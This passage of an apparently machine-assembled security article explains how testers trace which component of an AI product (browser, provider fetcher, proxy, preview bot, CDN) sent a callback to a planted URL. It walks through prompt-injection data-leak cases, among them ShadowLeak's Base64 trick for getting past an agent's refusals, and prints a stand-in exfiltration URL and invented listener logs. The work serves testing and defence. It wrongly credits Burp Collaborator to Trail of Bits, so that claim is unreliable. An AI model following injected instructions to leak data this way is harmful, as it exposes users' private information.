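# Attributing a callback to the component that fetched the URL in AI products

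## What a callback records and what can send one

AI products constantly fetch things from the web. A chatbot opens a page to answer a question, a browser loads a picture that the chatbot put in its reply, and a chat application downloads the title of a link that someone has just posted. Security testers use this behavior by planting a URL that leads to their own server, the *listener*, which records callbacks. A *callback* is a network request that reaches the listener because some component looked up or fetched the planted URL. Trail of Bits' *Burp Collaborator* describes a commercial listener that accepts web, DNS and mail traffic. A callback shows that something contacted the listener, but identifying what contacted it, and whose data or address leaked as a result, takes more work.

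Suppose a tester plants this URL, where `k7q2` marks one particular test:

```
https://k7q2.listener.example/i.png?d=VALUE
```

Some time later the listener writes this entry (invented, with an address from a block reserved for documentation):

```
203.0.113.24   05 Dec 2026 10:14:07 UTC   GET /i.png?d=blue-heron
User-Agent: Mozilla/5.0 ... compatible; ChatGPT-User/1.0 ...
Referer: (none)
```

The tester had stored the harmless marker "blue-heron" in a test mailbox, and a model with access to that mailbox has copied it into the URL. The cause is prompt injection, which is text in material a model reads that makes the model follow an outsider's instructions. The outsider's text, perhaps in a web page or an email, tells the model to add something private to a URL. Any component that then loads the URL delivers the data, because web servers routinely log the addresses that visitors request.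 OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that the load can happen in the background, through an embedded image or a link preview, so the user may never notice. The security blog Embrace The Red, which published *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, reported the problem to OpenAI in early 2023. Microsoft, whose Bing Chat had the same flaw, responded in May 2023 with a content security policy, a rule that tells the browser which hosts a web page may load images and other content from.

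### Fetcher, trigger and exposed party

The entry above involves three things that can vary independently, and summarising it as "ChatGPT leaked the mailbox" does not distinguish them. The *fetcher* is the component that opened the connection to the listener. The *trigger* is the event that made the fetcher act, such as a model's tool call, the display of a page or the posting of a message. The *exposed party* is the person or organisation whose data, network address or device details the callback reveals.

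Suppose the chatbot writes the planted URL into its answer as an image. If the chat page loads images directly, displaying the answer is the trigger and the reader's browser is the fetcher. This is a client-side fetch, made by software on a person's own device, and the listener receives the marker along with the reader's network address and some details of the device. If the product instead uses an image proxy, a server that downloads images on behalf of a viewer's browser, the trigger is the same, but the listener receives the marker with the proxy's address and no details of the reader's device.

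Other products never involve the reader's browser. If the model calls a browsing tool, the request comes from servers run by or for the AI provider (a provider-side fetch), and it can happen while nobody is looking at a screen. Chat platforms also fetch URLs to build link previews, the titles and pictures they show for links. Willison (2024) described how a chatbot with private data could leak it by posting a URL that the platform then fetches for its preview, and PromptArmor has since warned of the same problem with AI agents that people use through Slack or Telegram. In these cases, the source address (the IP address that connected to the listener) leads to the chat platform rather than to the owner of the data the bot could read.

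A user's data may have leaked even if the log shows a data-centre address. A callback with an empty `d=` field can still be harmful, because a browser that loads a planted image reveals its owner's network address.

### The DNS lookup

Before a component can connect to `k7q2.listener.example`, something has to translate that name into a numerical address through the Domain Name System (DNS). A tester who runs the domain's name server sees this lookup as a separate callback, usually just before the web request.

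The source address of a DNS lookup is a poor guide to what fetched the URL. Most software sends its lookups to a recursive resolver, a server that an internet provider, an employer or a public DNS company runs for many clients, and the resolver contacts the tester's name server. *Client Subnet in DNS Queries* (Contavalli, van der Gaast and colleagues, 2016) notes that resolvers can be far from their clients and describes an optional hint that lets a resolver forward part of the client's address. The hint normally covers only the client's network, senders can spoof it, and the document recommends that name server software leave the feature off by default. The resolver's own address is also fairly easy to fake, because most DNS traffic travels in single packets with no prior exchange to confirm the return address.

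Testers run into this regularly. In *Wrong lookup IP address in External service interaction (DNS)*, Anil (2021) asked whether a scanner's finding was a false alarm, because the lookup had come from an address outside the organisation's network. A resolver outside that network would explain the address without any error by the scanner. In *Strange DNS calls on the Burp Collaborator*, Mikhail (2020) reported that opening one planted name in a browser produced lookups from the internet provider's DNS server, as expected, and also from an address at Amazon's cloud service that Mikhail could not explain. Evidently, more than one party can look up the same name.

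Sometimes a DNS lookup arrives but no web request follows. PortSwigger's *Blind SSRF vulnerabilities* says this is common and typically happens because the application tried to connect, but network filtering blocked the web request while allowing DNS. The lookup can also have other causes, such as a security product that resolves every name it sees, so a DNS-only callback is weak evidence even that anything tried to fetch the URL.

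A DNS lookup carries only the host name from a URL, so it reveals data only if the data was in the host name. In the example, the listener's owner would learn that something had resolved `k7q2` but would not receive the marker "blue-heron", which is in the query string. If the model had put the marker in the host name, the lookup alone would have delivered it, even though the firewall blocked the web request.

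### Why the source address is hard to fake

A web request normally runs over TCP, which opens with a short exchange. The client sends a packet bearing its return address. The listener replies to that address with an unpredictable 32-bit number, and the client must acknowledge the number correctly before the connection opens. A machine that puts somebody else's address on its first packet never receives the reply, so it would have to guess one value out of about 4.3 billion. HTTPS then requires a cryptographic exchange over the same connection, which a sender working blind cannot complete. (The newest version of HTTP uses QUIC instead of TCP, but its handshake also depends on replies getting back to the client.)

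When a request completes, something at its source address has therefore received the listener's packets. Faking the address would require control of a machine there or of the route to it. This makes the address the most reliable item in the entry, but it identifies only the last machine to open a connection, and testers often want to know more than that. The machine may be a VPN exit, an office gateway shared by thousands of people, or a rented server. Sullivan (2023) reports in *Introducing CoWitness* that many of his callbacks came from an Akamai or Cloudflare device in front of the application under test rather than from the application's own server.

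An IP address at a large operator also doesn't identify an individual user. OpenAI's *IP egress ranges* states that a match identifies an OpenAI-operated network, "not a specific user or workspace". One task can also use several addresses. In the forum post *Can anyone explain this ChatGPT / OpenAI file-request behavior?*, website owner SumGuy (2026) describes what looked like a single ChatGPT-User session that requested 13 files in 50 seconds from different addresses. Counting addresses in that case would have overstated the number of fetchers.

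### Headers and other traits of the request

The requesting software writes the headers, and anyone with a command-line tool can write the same ones. Unlike the source address, nothing in the exchange checks them. A signed request is the exception, because it carries a cryptographic signature that the tester can check against a key the operator publishes, as Cloudflare's *Bot Information for ChatGPT agent* records for OpenAI's browsing agent. Unsigned headers can't establish an attribution on their own, but they can support one, because the product under test usually has no reason to deceive its tester and a forger who copies one header often neglects the others.

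The **user agent** is the text in which the requesting software names itself. The HTTP standard from the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF) recommends that software send one and not use other products' names, but it can't enforce either recommendation. Cloudflare tells site owners not to identify its own hosted browser by this header, since any client can send any text. Wright's *Verify GPTBot IP* cites a January 2026 analysis by the security company HUMAN, which found that 5.7% of traffic with AI crawlers' user agents was fake, rising to about one request in six for ChatGPT-User. A genuine user agent can also be misread. OpenAI's example for its search crawler, OAI-SearchBot, begins like Chrome on a Mac and includes the crawler's name only near the end.

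**Accept and related headers** list the file types, compression methods and languages the fetcher prefers. A browser loading an image tends to name modern picture formats, whereas a simple program may accept anything or leave the field out. *Request Info Logger*, a tool that displays what an image load reveals, notes that browsers differ in the combination and order they send, and that a VPN doesn't change the language list. A preference for Swiss German in a callback from an American data centre suggests that a person is somewhere behind the connection, if the header has not been faked.

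Browsers use the **Referer** header (a historical misspelling of "referrer") to send the address of the page that led to the request. A chat product's web address in this header suggests that the request came from a browser that displayed that page. A missing header is much weaker evidence about the sender. The IETF's standard lets software shorten the value to the site's address alone, and requires software to omit it or send a blank placeholder when a person types the URL. The standard notes that some intermediaries remove it. Imgix's *Understanding User Agents and Referers* also lists private browsing and browser privacy settings as reasons the header may be missing.

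**Via.** The IETF's standard requires a proxy that forwards a request to add an entry to this header, so a chain of proxies leaves an ordered list. The operator may substitute a pseudonym for the host's real name. A proxy that only tunnels an encrypted connection, as on many corporate networks, adds nothing, so a missing Via header does not rule out a proxy. The standard also forbids a forwarding proxy from altering the path or query string. This rule is more useful to testers, because the test's identifier and the marker should arrive intact even when the headers have changed.

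**Sec-Fetch headers** describe the context of a browser's request. According to W3C's *Fetch Metadata Request Headers* (2025), an image that a page loads from another site produces the values `image`, `no-cors` and `cross-site`. A clicked link produces `document` and `navigate`, plus a fourth header, Sec-Fetch-User, that marks a user's action. The site value is `none` when someone types the address or opens a bookmark, according to MDN's *Fetch metadata*. These headers are unusually useful because they come close to recording what triggered the request. Scripts on a web page cannot change them, but a program outside the browser can set them to any value. Browsers send them only to secure addresses, so a tester who plants a plain `http` link loses this evidence.

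Most crawlers do not send Sec-Fetch headers. In a September 2026 probe, http.dev's *Sec-Fetch-Site* found the header missing from 14 of 16 verified crawlers, including GPTBot, ClaudeBot and Googlebot. Two Meta crawlers sent it sometimes. The 16 do not include ChatGPT-User or Claude-User, which fetch pages at a user's request and which testers of AI products are more likely to meet, so the finding may not apply to them. The headers also do not prove that a human made the request, because an AI agent that drives a real browser sends that browser's headers.

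Chrome and related browsers also send client hints, which are separate headers that repeat the browser's brand, platform and mobile status and give more detail if the server asks for it. An HTTPS request with a recent Chrome user agent but no client hints is suspicious, though a careful forger would include them.

**TLS fingerprint.** When a client opens an encrypted connection, it lists the protocol versions, ciphers and extensions it supports. The networking library determines that list, so a script that changes its user agent to "Chrome" will usually still send a list typical of a script. Specialised tools can imitate a browser's list, so this trait is harder to forge than a header but far from impossible. Like other browser traits, it may also fail to distinguish one agent from another. *FP-Agent* (2026), a study that covered seven AI browsing agents, found that browser fingerprints separated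 them poorly when several agents shared a fingerprint. Typing, scrolling and mouse movements did distinguish the agents from people and from one another in that study, but a single image load involves none of these.

The listener records a callback's **time of arrival** from its own clock, so the sender can delay a request but cannot change the recorded time. A callback that arrives two seconds after a chatbot replies suggests a different trigger from one that arrives overnight. Embrace The Red cautions that requests may arrive out of order and that browsers cache what they load, so displaying an image a second time may not produce another callback. Testers can learn more from timing by measuring round trips or repeating the test under controlled conditions.

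A diagnostic page on OpenAI's login host shows how much of this a server keeps. On 4 April 2026, it listed one visit's source address, user agent (which named Anthropic's ClaudeBot), time to a hundredth of a second, country, HTTP version (HTTP/2), TLS version (1.3) and key-exchange method. The visitor supplied the name "ClaudeBot" itself, so any check of whether Anthropic sent the request would have to start from the address.

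### Tying an address to an operator

Regional internet registries keep public records of who holds each block of addresses, and routing data identifies the network that announces the block to the rest of the internet by its autonomous system number. These two lookups work for any address and quickly distinguish a home broadband line from a data centre, but they often identify only the cloud provider and not the customer using the address. *ChatGPT / openai bot* (SumGuy, 2024) reports an early ChatGPT-User visit from an address that belonged to Microsoft and had no host name. Thousands of Microsoft's cloud customers could show up the same way.

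A published range, a list of IP addresses that an operator says its fetcher uses, closes part of that gap. The operator writes each block of addresses as a prefix, such as a /28, which covers 16 addresses, or a /22, which covers 1,024. OpenAI publishes separate files for each of its crawlers, ChatGPT-User, ChatGPT's connections to outside services and its cloud coding agent. Anthropic states that a crawler with an address on its list comes from Anthropic. PPC Land, a marketing trade publication, counted 23 prefixes on that list in August 2026. All were in Google's and Microsoft's clouds, and no label showed which of Anthropic's three robots used which prefix. Anthropic's *Inbound IP addresses* gives a separate range for the company's other services, a fixed /23 for traffic in both directions. A tester who checks only one of these lists may therefore wrongly rule Anthropic out.

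An address match is strong evidence of the operator but weaker evidence of the product. Wright found that some prefixes appear in OpenAI's files for both GPTBot and OAI-SearchBot. When an address falls in one of these shared prefixes, the user agent becomes useful again, because the address has already ruled out other operators and the header is needed only to tell one OpenAI fetcher from another.

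An IP address's absence from a vendor's published ranges proves little, because the lists lag behind the addresses in use. In *[bug] unpublished IP addresses*, a thread on OpenAI's developer forum, a site operator listed eleven ranges that were sending requests with the user agent of OpenAI's connectors but did not appear in the company's file. OpenAI replied that a refresh on 8 July 2026 now covered them all. Before the refresh, a check against the file would have wrongly ruled out OpenAI as the source of those requests. It is sensible to save a copy of the range file on the day of the test and to recheck any unmatched addresses later.

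Reverse DNS offers an independent check for operators that support it. Google sets out the steps:

1. Look up the host name for the source address. For 66.249.66.1 this gives `crawl-66-249-66-1.googlebot.com`.
2. Check that the name ends in one of Google's domains.
3. Look up the address for that host name, and confirm that it is the one in the log.

Step 3 is essential because whoever controls a block of addresses also controls the host names that a reverse lookup returns, and could enter a Google name for a machine that has nothing to do with Google. Only Google can make `googlebot.com` point back to that machine. Google (2006) warned site owners that the reverse lookup alone could be spoofed. Names under `gae.googleusercontent.com` also need care, because they can belong to features that Google's cloud customers run on their own sites. The method also depends on the operator's cooperation.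 According to Wright, OpenAI documents no such host names, so range files are the main check on its unsigned requests.

### When a CDN stands in front of the listener

All of this assumes that the fetcher connects to the listener directly. Many testers host listeners behind a content delivery network (CDN) or a load balancer, which accepts the fetcher's connection and opens a second one to the listener. The same request then looks like this:

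```
Direct:        source address    203.0.113.24

Behind a CDN:  source address    198.51.100.7
               X-Forwarded-For   203.0.113.24
               Via               1.1 edge
```

When the listener is behind a CDN, it logs the CDN's IP address and TLS fingerprint instead of the fetcher's. The fetcher's address is in a header, such as Cloudflare's CF-Connecting-IP. A tester who overlooks this could attribute every callback to the CDN, or mistake the CDN's Via entry for a sign of an image proxy on the product's side.

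The forwarded address is only as reliable as the machine that wrote it. A sender can include its own X-Forwarded-For header, and many CDNs append the true address to it, so with a single CDN in the path, the last entry is the one to use. If the listener also accepts direct connections, a sender can bypass the CDN and invent the whole header. Testers can prevent this by accepting connections only from the CDN's addresses. They should also turn off the CDN's caching and bot blocking, since either can keep a callback from reaching the listener. The simplest setup is a server with its own name server and nothing in front of it.

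### The possible fetchers

Cloudflare's *Bot reference* sorts AI companies' bots into crawlers, search bots and assistants. Several other kinds of fetcher can also request a planted URL.

| Fetcher | Holder of the source address | Usual trigger |
|---|---|---|
| A person's browser or app | The person's home, office or mobile network | An image appears on screen, or the person clicks |
| Provider's page fetcher (ChatGPT-User, Claude-User) | The AI provider or its cloud host | A user's question or a model's tool call |
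| Provider's crawler (GPTBot, ClaudeBot) | The AI provider or its cloud host | Automatic crawling of public pages |
| Browser hosted by the provider (ChatGPT agent, Claude-Agent) | The AI provider or its cloud host | A step in an agent's task |
| Provider's connector to outside services | The AI provider or its cloud host | A model's tool call |
| Image proxy | The proxy's operator | A viewer's browser displays an image |
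| Link preview bot | The chat platform | A person or a bot posts a link |
| Coding agent on a developer's machine | The developer's network | A tool call or a command |
| Coding agent in the cloud | The AI provider or its cloud host | A tool call or a command |
| Security scanner or filter | A security company, a CDN or an employer | Inspection of a message or request that contains the URL |

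## A person's browser: the OpenAI API log viewer

A person's own browser is the simplest fetcher to understand. In *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend* (December 2025), veganmosfet built a small retrieval chatbot, which searches a collection of documents for passages relevant to a question and gives them to the model. The chatbot ran on dify, an open-source platform for applications that use language models. One of the two PDF files in the collection contained a hidden prompt injection. When the user asked about that file's topic, the model wrote an image into its answer in Markdown, a simple notation for formatting text, and put the user's name in the image's URL. Dify's chat page rendered the image, so the user's browser requested it from an outside server. By default the page had no content security policy for images, so the browser would load them from any host.

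In this case, the person who asked the question also owned the leaked name and ran the browser that leaked it, so the address in the listener's log belongs to the person whose data is in the URL.

### An answer that the application blocked

PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs*, published in January 2026, describes a case where the address and the data belong to different people. PromptArmor built a mock version of the tools banks use to check customers' identities. Its assistant ran on OpenAI's API, the interface through which other companies' software uses OpenAI's models. The attack went as follows:

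1. The user asks the assistant about a customer. The application gathers six sources of data, one of which contains text from the web with a prompt injection in it.
2. The model follows the injected text. It writes a Markdown image whose URL leads to the outsider's server and contains the customer's personal and financial details.
3. A second model, which checks answers before the user sees them, flags this one, and the application blocks it. No browser has loaded the image yet.
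4. A developer investigates the flagged conversation in OpenAI's API log viewer, a web page where OpenAI's business customers can read what their applications sent and received.
5. The log viewer displays the answer as formatted Markdown. The developer's browser requests the image, and the outsider's server records the full URL.

The application's filter worked, but it also gave the developer a reason to open the conversation.

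| | Retrieval chatbot | API log viewer |
|---|---|---|
| Fetcher | The user's browser | The developer's browser |
| Trigger | The answer appears in the chat | The developer opens the stored conversation |
| Data in the URL | The user's name | Records from the user's session |
| Address in the log | The user's | The developer's |

A tester who assumes the address is the user's will misjudge who is exposed. The leaked data is the user's (here, records about the customer under review), but the address and browser details are those of a developer with access to the application's logs. The tester may also report the bug to the wrong company, because OpenAI's page loaded the image. Timing can help the tester avoid this mistake, because the listener records nothing when the application blocks the answer, and the callback arrives when somebody reviews the conversation, perhaps days later.

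An application that strips images from its answers or shows them as plain text has the same gap, because the stored answer still contains the image. In PromptArmor's example, the AI search product Perplexity removed the image from a test answer, which left an oddly empty reply. A user might give such a reply a thumbs-down, and a developer investigating the complaint could then load the image. PromptArmor showed the empty reply but not anyone at Perplexity reviewing it, so this part of the argument is only plausible.

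PromptArmor found the same flaw in the previews where developers try out chats, assistants and agents before release, and in several of OpenAI's ChatKit tools for building chat interfaces. In a preview, the browser and the test conversation usually belong to the same developer. Other companies' developer tools have had the same flaw. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground* covers one case, and Willison's *Google AI Studio data exfiltration demo* (2024) covers another, in which the test data was a file of employee reviews. The browser in that demo belonged to the person who uploaded the file, but the data was about the employees.

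PromptArmor reported the log viewer flaw on 17 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that screens vulnerability reports for OpenAI. PromptArmor supplied steps to reproduce the problem and answered three rounds of questions, but the report was closed as "Not applicable" on 4 December without OpenAI having seen it. After PromptArmor published the article, OpenAI confirmed the flaw, and on 22 January 2026 it reopened the report and indicated that a fix was under way. PromptArmor's timeline ends there and records no completed fix, so testers should check whether the log viewer still loads outside images before counting it among the possible fetchers.

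### The 2023 reports and content security policy

The underlying problem was nearly three years old by then. Johann Rehberger, who writes Embrace The Red, reported it to Microsoft on 8 April 2023 and to OpenAI the next day. His post *Bing Chat* explains how a comment or an advertisement on a web page could set off the leak in Microsoft's chatbot. *ChatGPT Plugins*, another of his posts, credits Roman Samoilenko with finding the flaw in ChatGPT a few days before Rehberger did. OpenAI told Rehberger that loading images was a feature and that it planned no changes. Microsoft notified him of a fix on 15 June, although his 2026 retrospective dates the fix to May.

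The visible part of Microsoft's fix was a content security policy that allowed images only from four Bing hosts. If the model writes an image from any other host, the browser blocks the request and the listener records nothing. The browser's developer console shows the block, so a tester can distinguish a blocked image from one the model never wrote.

A content security policy applies only to the page it is sent with. Even if the bank's application had used the strictest possible policy, OpenAI's log viewer would still have displayed the stored answer under its own rules.

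A policy can also fail because of a host it allows. The email product Superhuman accepted images from `docs.google.com`, which also hosts Google Forms. Willison reported in January 2026 that a prompt injection in an email used this access to submit the contents of other emails to an outsider's Google Form. The data went to Google's servers, so a listener on the tester's domain would have recorded nothing. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes a similar gap in OpenAI's URL check, which accepted addresses at Microsoft's cloud storage service. Rehberger opened a storage account there and read the callbacks in its logs.

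Scripts can also get around a policy. Willison (2026), in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*, summarises an attack by Parameter Labs on people who opened a shared ChatGPT link while signed in. ChatGPT's policy allowed scripts from YouTube, and the researchers used that exception to run their own code. The code collected the visitor's private data and sent it out in an image request. OpenAI has since fixed the vulnerability.

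### An image load and a click, header by header

Suppose a developer using Chrome on a Mac opens the log viewer, and the page loads the planted image. The request would look roughly like this (an invented example based on browsers' defaults):

```
GET /i.png?d=blue-heron
User-Agent: Mozilla/5.0 (Macintosh; ...) ... Chrome/[version].0.0.0 ...
Accept: image/avif,image/webp,image/apng,image/svg+xml,image/*,*/*;q=0.8
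Referer: https://platform.openai.com/
Sec-Fetch-Dest: image
Sec-Fetch-Mode: no-cors
Sec-Fetch-Site: cross-site
Sec-CH-UA-Platform: "macOS"
Sec-CH-UA-Mobile: ?0
```

Nothing here is specific to developers, and apart from the Referer, a user with the same browser would send the same headers. If the page had shown a planted link and the developer had clicked it, several headers would be different:

| Header | Image that the page loads | Link that a person clicks |
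|---|---|---|
| Sec-Fetch-Dest | `image` | `document` |
| Sec-Fetch-Mode | `no-cors` | `navigate` |
| Sec-Fetch-Site | `cross-site` | `cross-site` |
| Sec-Fetch-User | Absent | `?1` |
| Accept | Begins with image formats | Begins with `text/html` |
| Referer | The page's site address, unless suppressed | The same |
| Client hints (Chrome and Edge) | Brand, platform and mobile status | The same |

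Sec-Fetch-Dest is the quickest way to tell an image load from a click, but Sec-Fetch-Site can't distinguish them because both requests come from a page on another site. A request for a `document` without Sec-Fetch-User suggests that a script opened the address. According to W3C, Safari began sending Sec-Fetch headers in March 2023, after Chrome and Firefox, so an HTTPS request that lacks them needs explaining if its User-Agent names a current browser.

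The beginning of the **Accept** header is more informative than the rest. MDN's *Accept header* shows that browsers list `text/html` first when they open a page and image formats first when they load a picture. Searching the log for `image/webp` would give misleading results. dholbert notes in *Consider including `image/webp` in initial `accept` header sent to websites* that Chrome includes that format even when it requests a web page, whereas Firefox does not.

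The full list can also help check the user agent. When Gosu compared image requests in February 2024, only Chrome listed APNG and only Safari listed HEIC. Browser makers change these lists, so it is best to compare a callback with a fresh request from the same browser version. Wilde (2026) reported that by January 2026 all three major browsers included AVIF and WebP, neither of which was in the web standard's default.

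The **Referer** header is the most likely to distinguish the application from the log viewer. Under the default described in MDN's *Referrer-Policy header*, a browser loading an image from another site sends only the page's origin, meaning its scheme and host name. The listener would receive `https://platform.openai.com/` from the log viewer and the bank's address from the application. The header would not show which conversation the developer had opened. If the planted URL begins with `http://` and the page uses HTTPS, the browser sends no Referer. A page can also suppress the header for everything it loads or for a single image.

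Firefox and Safari do not send client hints, according to Web Platform DX's *User agent client hints*. The platform hint gives the operating system's name but not its version, and Chrome no longer puts the real version in its user agent either, according to http.dev's *Sec-CH-UA*.

A server can ask Chrome for extra client hints, such as the device model, but Chromium's *Life of Client Hint* explains that the browser stores this request only when it arrives with a page opened over a secure connection. A listener can therefore obtain the device model this way when it receives a click, but not when it has only served an image. If the listener marks the extra hints as critical, Chrome immediately repeats the page request with the hints added, so one click appears in the log as two requests.

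Many web servers log only some of a request's headers. Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT* shows log lines from September 2023 that include the user agent and the Referer but no other headers. Testers who want the other headers need to configure the listener to record them before the test.

Those lines also show how easily requests from two fetchers can end up in one set of results. Rehberger was testing images in ChatGPT's replies, and two of the requests have a user agent for Firefox on a Mac. Their Referer is empty. By default, the browser would have included ChatGPT's address, so the chat page or a browser setting probably suppressed it. A third request, from the same afternoon, has the ChatGPT-User user agent. The post presents it as another image load, but the user agent suggests that it came from OpenAI's servers. The source address could confirm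 this, but Rehberger redacted it.

None of these headers describe the viewer's browser when a proxy relays the image.

### Missing and reordered requests

Browser caching can result in fewer callbacks than the number of times someone saw the image. The listener can forbid caching by sending the instruction `Cache-Control: no-store` with the image, but this has limits.

The HTML standard requires browsers to keep a list of the images already available in an open page. One purpose of the list, according to a passage quoted in a bug report from WebKit, the engine behind Safari, is to avoid downloading an image again even when caching is forbidden. Chrome used to make a new request when a script assigned the same URL to an image again. Januschka (2026), in *Web-Facing Change PSA*, announced a change to make Chrome match Firefox and Safari, so the same test may produce fewer callbacks in newer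 versions of Chrome. Two images with the same URL can also share a download still in progress, as Pieters and Nottingham (2014) discussed while clarifying the standard.

Reloading the log viewer starts a new page with an empty list, so it should produce a new callback if the listener forbids caching. The major browsers also keep separate caches for separate websites, so the listener should receive two requests if a tester displays an image in the application and then opens the log viewer in the same browser.

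The order of callbacks is also unreliable. A browser requests several images at once, so the request for the third image on the page may reach the listener before the request for the first. Some pages wait to load an image until the reader scrolls near it, which could delay or prevent a callback from a long conversation. These effects also limit an attacker who tries to leak a word with one image per letter, because the letters may arrive in the wrong order and the browser may request a repeated letter only once.

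Testers can avoid most of this confusion by giving every planted image its own identifier. But they cannot use the identifier to tell whether the application or the log viewer fetched the image, because both display the same stored answer with the same URL. To distinguish those two, they need the Referer, the source address or a record of when each page was open.

### Desktop and mobile apps

An app on a person's device can make a client-side fetch that looks different from a browser's. Many desktop apps use Electron, a framework that combines a web page with Chrome's engine. Electron's default user agent resembles Chrome's but adds the app's name and the word `Electron`.

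Android apps can display web content through WebView, a browser component built into the system. WebView changes the list of browser brands in the client hints. If an app replaces the user agent without supplying matching details, Chromium sends no user agent hints. Missing hints may therefore only mean that the person was using an app, although they would be suspicious in a request from Chrome itself.

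Other apps download images without a browser engine. On an iPhone, the user agent typically consists of the app's name followed by `CFNetwork` and `Darwin`, the names of Apple's networking library and the core of its operating system. On Android it is often `okhttp`, the name of a popular networking library. These requests usually lack Sec-Fetch headers and a Referer, so they can look like they came from a script. A source address on a home or mobile network makes it more likely that they came from a person's app. The tester can confirm this by displaying a new image in the same app and comparing the two requests.

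The app can also affect whether a callback happens. In December 2023 OpenAI introduced a check on image URLs, a forerunner of its present check against a public index, but only in ChatGPT's web client. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* found that the iOS app lacked the check, so an answer that produced no callback on the website could still produce one there.

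## The provider's browsing service: ShadowLeak and ChatGPT

A chatbot that can open web pages can leak data without involving anyone's browser. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes such a leak from Deep Research, a mode of ChatGPT that spends five to 30 minutes reading sources and then writes a report. Users can let it read a Gmail mailbox as well as the web. In 2025 Radware, a security company, showed that one email in the mailbox could make the agent send personal data to an outside server. The attack went as follows:

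1. The outsider sends the user an email that looks like routine office correspondence. Its HTML hides instructions for the agent, for example as white text on a white background.
2. The mailbox also contains a genuine email from the personnel department with an employee's name and address.
3. The user asks Deep Research to go through the day's emails for information about a new employee.
4. The agent reads both emails. It follows the hidden instructions, encodes the name and address, and opens a URL that contains them.
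5. The outsider's server records the request. The user has not opened the email or clicked anything.

Radware's first attempts failed. The agent refused plain instructions to send the data, and it treated the URL as suspicious and searched for it online instead of opening it. When the instructions named the agent's page-opening tool and told it to keep trying, requests began to reach the server, but some arrived without the data, so a tester who stopped there would have had a callback but no leak. The final version had the agent encode the data in Base64, a standard way of writing any data as letters, digits and a few symbols. According to Radware, the software that ran the tool then received only a harmless-looking string.

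Radware reports a 100% success rate "in repeated tests" but doesn't say how many tests it ran. If it ran ten, for example, a perfect result would still be compatible with a true success rate as low as about 74% (the lower limit at 95% confidence).

Radware reported the flaw through Bugcrowd on 18 June 2025 and sent a more reliable version of the attack the next day. OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August without telling Radware, then acknowledged it and marked it resolved on 3 September. A Radware spokesperson said the company had not seen anyone exploit it, according to The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent*.

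### Did the request come from OpenAI's cloud?

Radware says OpenAI's browsing service fetched the URL, but the text of its report gives no source address or user agent. The conclusion is based on how the attack worked.

The data in the URL is the most useful evidence. The planted email contained only a URL template with a gap for the employee's details. A mail scanner that followed links in the email could have contacted the server, but could not have filled the gap with details from a different message. A model with access to both emails must have composed the URL.

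That doesn't establish which component fetched the URL. Radware learned about the page-opening tool by asking the agent what tools it had, which is weak evidence on its own because models can describe their tools incorrectly. But requests began arriving when the instructions told the agent to use that tool, and arrived more often when they told it to retry. Radware also reports that the chat page displayed nothing a browser could have loaded. Since Deep Research runs on OpenAI's servers, a request from its browsing tool should come from there too.

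This is convincing evidence of a provider-side fetch. It is weaker evidence of whose machine opened the connection, because a provider can run its browsing through a contractor. In its statement to The Record, OpenAI confirmed that it had received Radware's report of the bug through its bounty programme, but did not discuss the route the data took.

A log entry could have helped settle the matter. Suppose a tester repeats the experiment with the marker "blue-heron" and the listener records this (an invented entry):

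```
198.51.100.37   10:21:44 UTC   GET /k7q2/Ymx1ZS1oZXJvbg==
User-Agent: Mozilla/5.0 AppleWebKit/537.36 (KHTML, like Gecko);
            compatible; ChatGPT-User/1.0; ...
Referer: (none)
```

A source address in one of OpenAI's published ranges would show that OpenAI operated the fetcher, and the user agent would suggest which service made the request. The timing could also rule out the tester's browser or computer. A request that arrives ten minutes before the finished report appears cannot come from a browser displaying that report, although the tester should check that the progress display loads nothing from the planted site. A callback that arrives while the tester's computer is switched off cannot come from that computer.

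Searching the log only for "blue-heron" can also miss a leak. In this entry, the string at the end of the path is the same marker in Base64. It is best to search for both forms and leave out the closing equals signs, which some software rewrites.

Radware announced ShadowLeak as the first purely server-side leak of sensitive data. The ChatGPT-User request that Rehberger logged in September 2023 may be an earlier example, but this is uncertain without the request's source address.

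### OpenAI's identities and address files

To check an address against OpenAI's files, a tester has to know which service each file covers.

| OpenAI service | What prompts a request | Address file |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT-User | A user's question or other action in ChatGPT or a custom GPT | `chatgpt-user.json` |
| OAI-SearchBot | Automatic crawling for ChatGPT's search results | `searchbot.json` |
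| GPTBot | Automatic crawling for material that may train models | `gptbot.json` |
| OAI-AdsBot | An advertiser submits a page as a ChatGPT ad | `adsbot.json` |
| Plugins, connectors and GPT Actions | ChatGPT contacts an outside service | `chatgpt-connectors.json` |
| Codex cloud, the hosted coding agent | The agent connects to a service such as GitHub | `chatgpt-agents.json` |

A ShadowLeak request would most likely use the ChatGPT-User identity, because the fetch results from a user's prompt. But OpenAI says only that it uses this identity for "certain user actions", and its list does not mention Deep Research, so a tester should check the address against all of OpenAI's address files before ruling OpenAI out.

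The connectors file is easy to misapply in a case like this one. When Deep Research reads a Gmail mailbox, the connector contacts Google, so the tester's listener receives only the later request from the browsing tool. The connectors file applies when the tester runs the outside service that ChatGPT connects to. GPT Actions, which let a custom GPT call such a service, appear in both the description of ChatGPT-User and the list of products that use the connectors file, so the tester needs to check their requests against both.

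The last file's name, `chatgpt-agents.json`, is also misleading. OpenAI says the file covers Codex cloud. ChatGPT agent, the browsing agent, is identified separately by its signed requests.

If a site allows both GPTBot and OAI-SearchBot, OpenAI may crawl a page once and use the result for both training and search. A GPTBot request in the log therefore identifies the crawler that visited, but doesn't necessarily mean that OpenAI wanted the page for training.

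### Matching an address to a range

msandersfresha (2026), in *[bug] unpublished IP addresses*, reported connections to a chat app from several addresses, including 172.170.1.82. Another participant in the thread listed the range 172.170.1.80/28. This CIDR notation gives a starting address and the number of leading bits that every address in the range shares.

An IPv4 address has 32 bits, written as four numbers of eight bits each. A /28 fixes the first 28 and leaves four free, which gives 2⁴ = 16 addresses. The first three numbers account for 24 of the fixed bits, so the other four are the first half of the last number:

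```
Range start   172.170.1.80    last number in binary: 0101 0000
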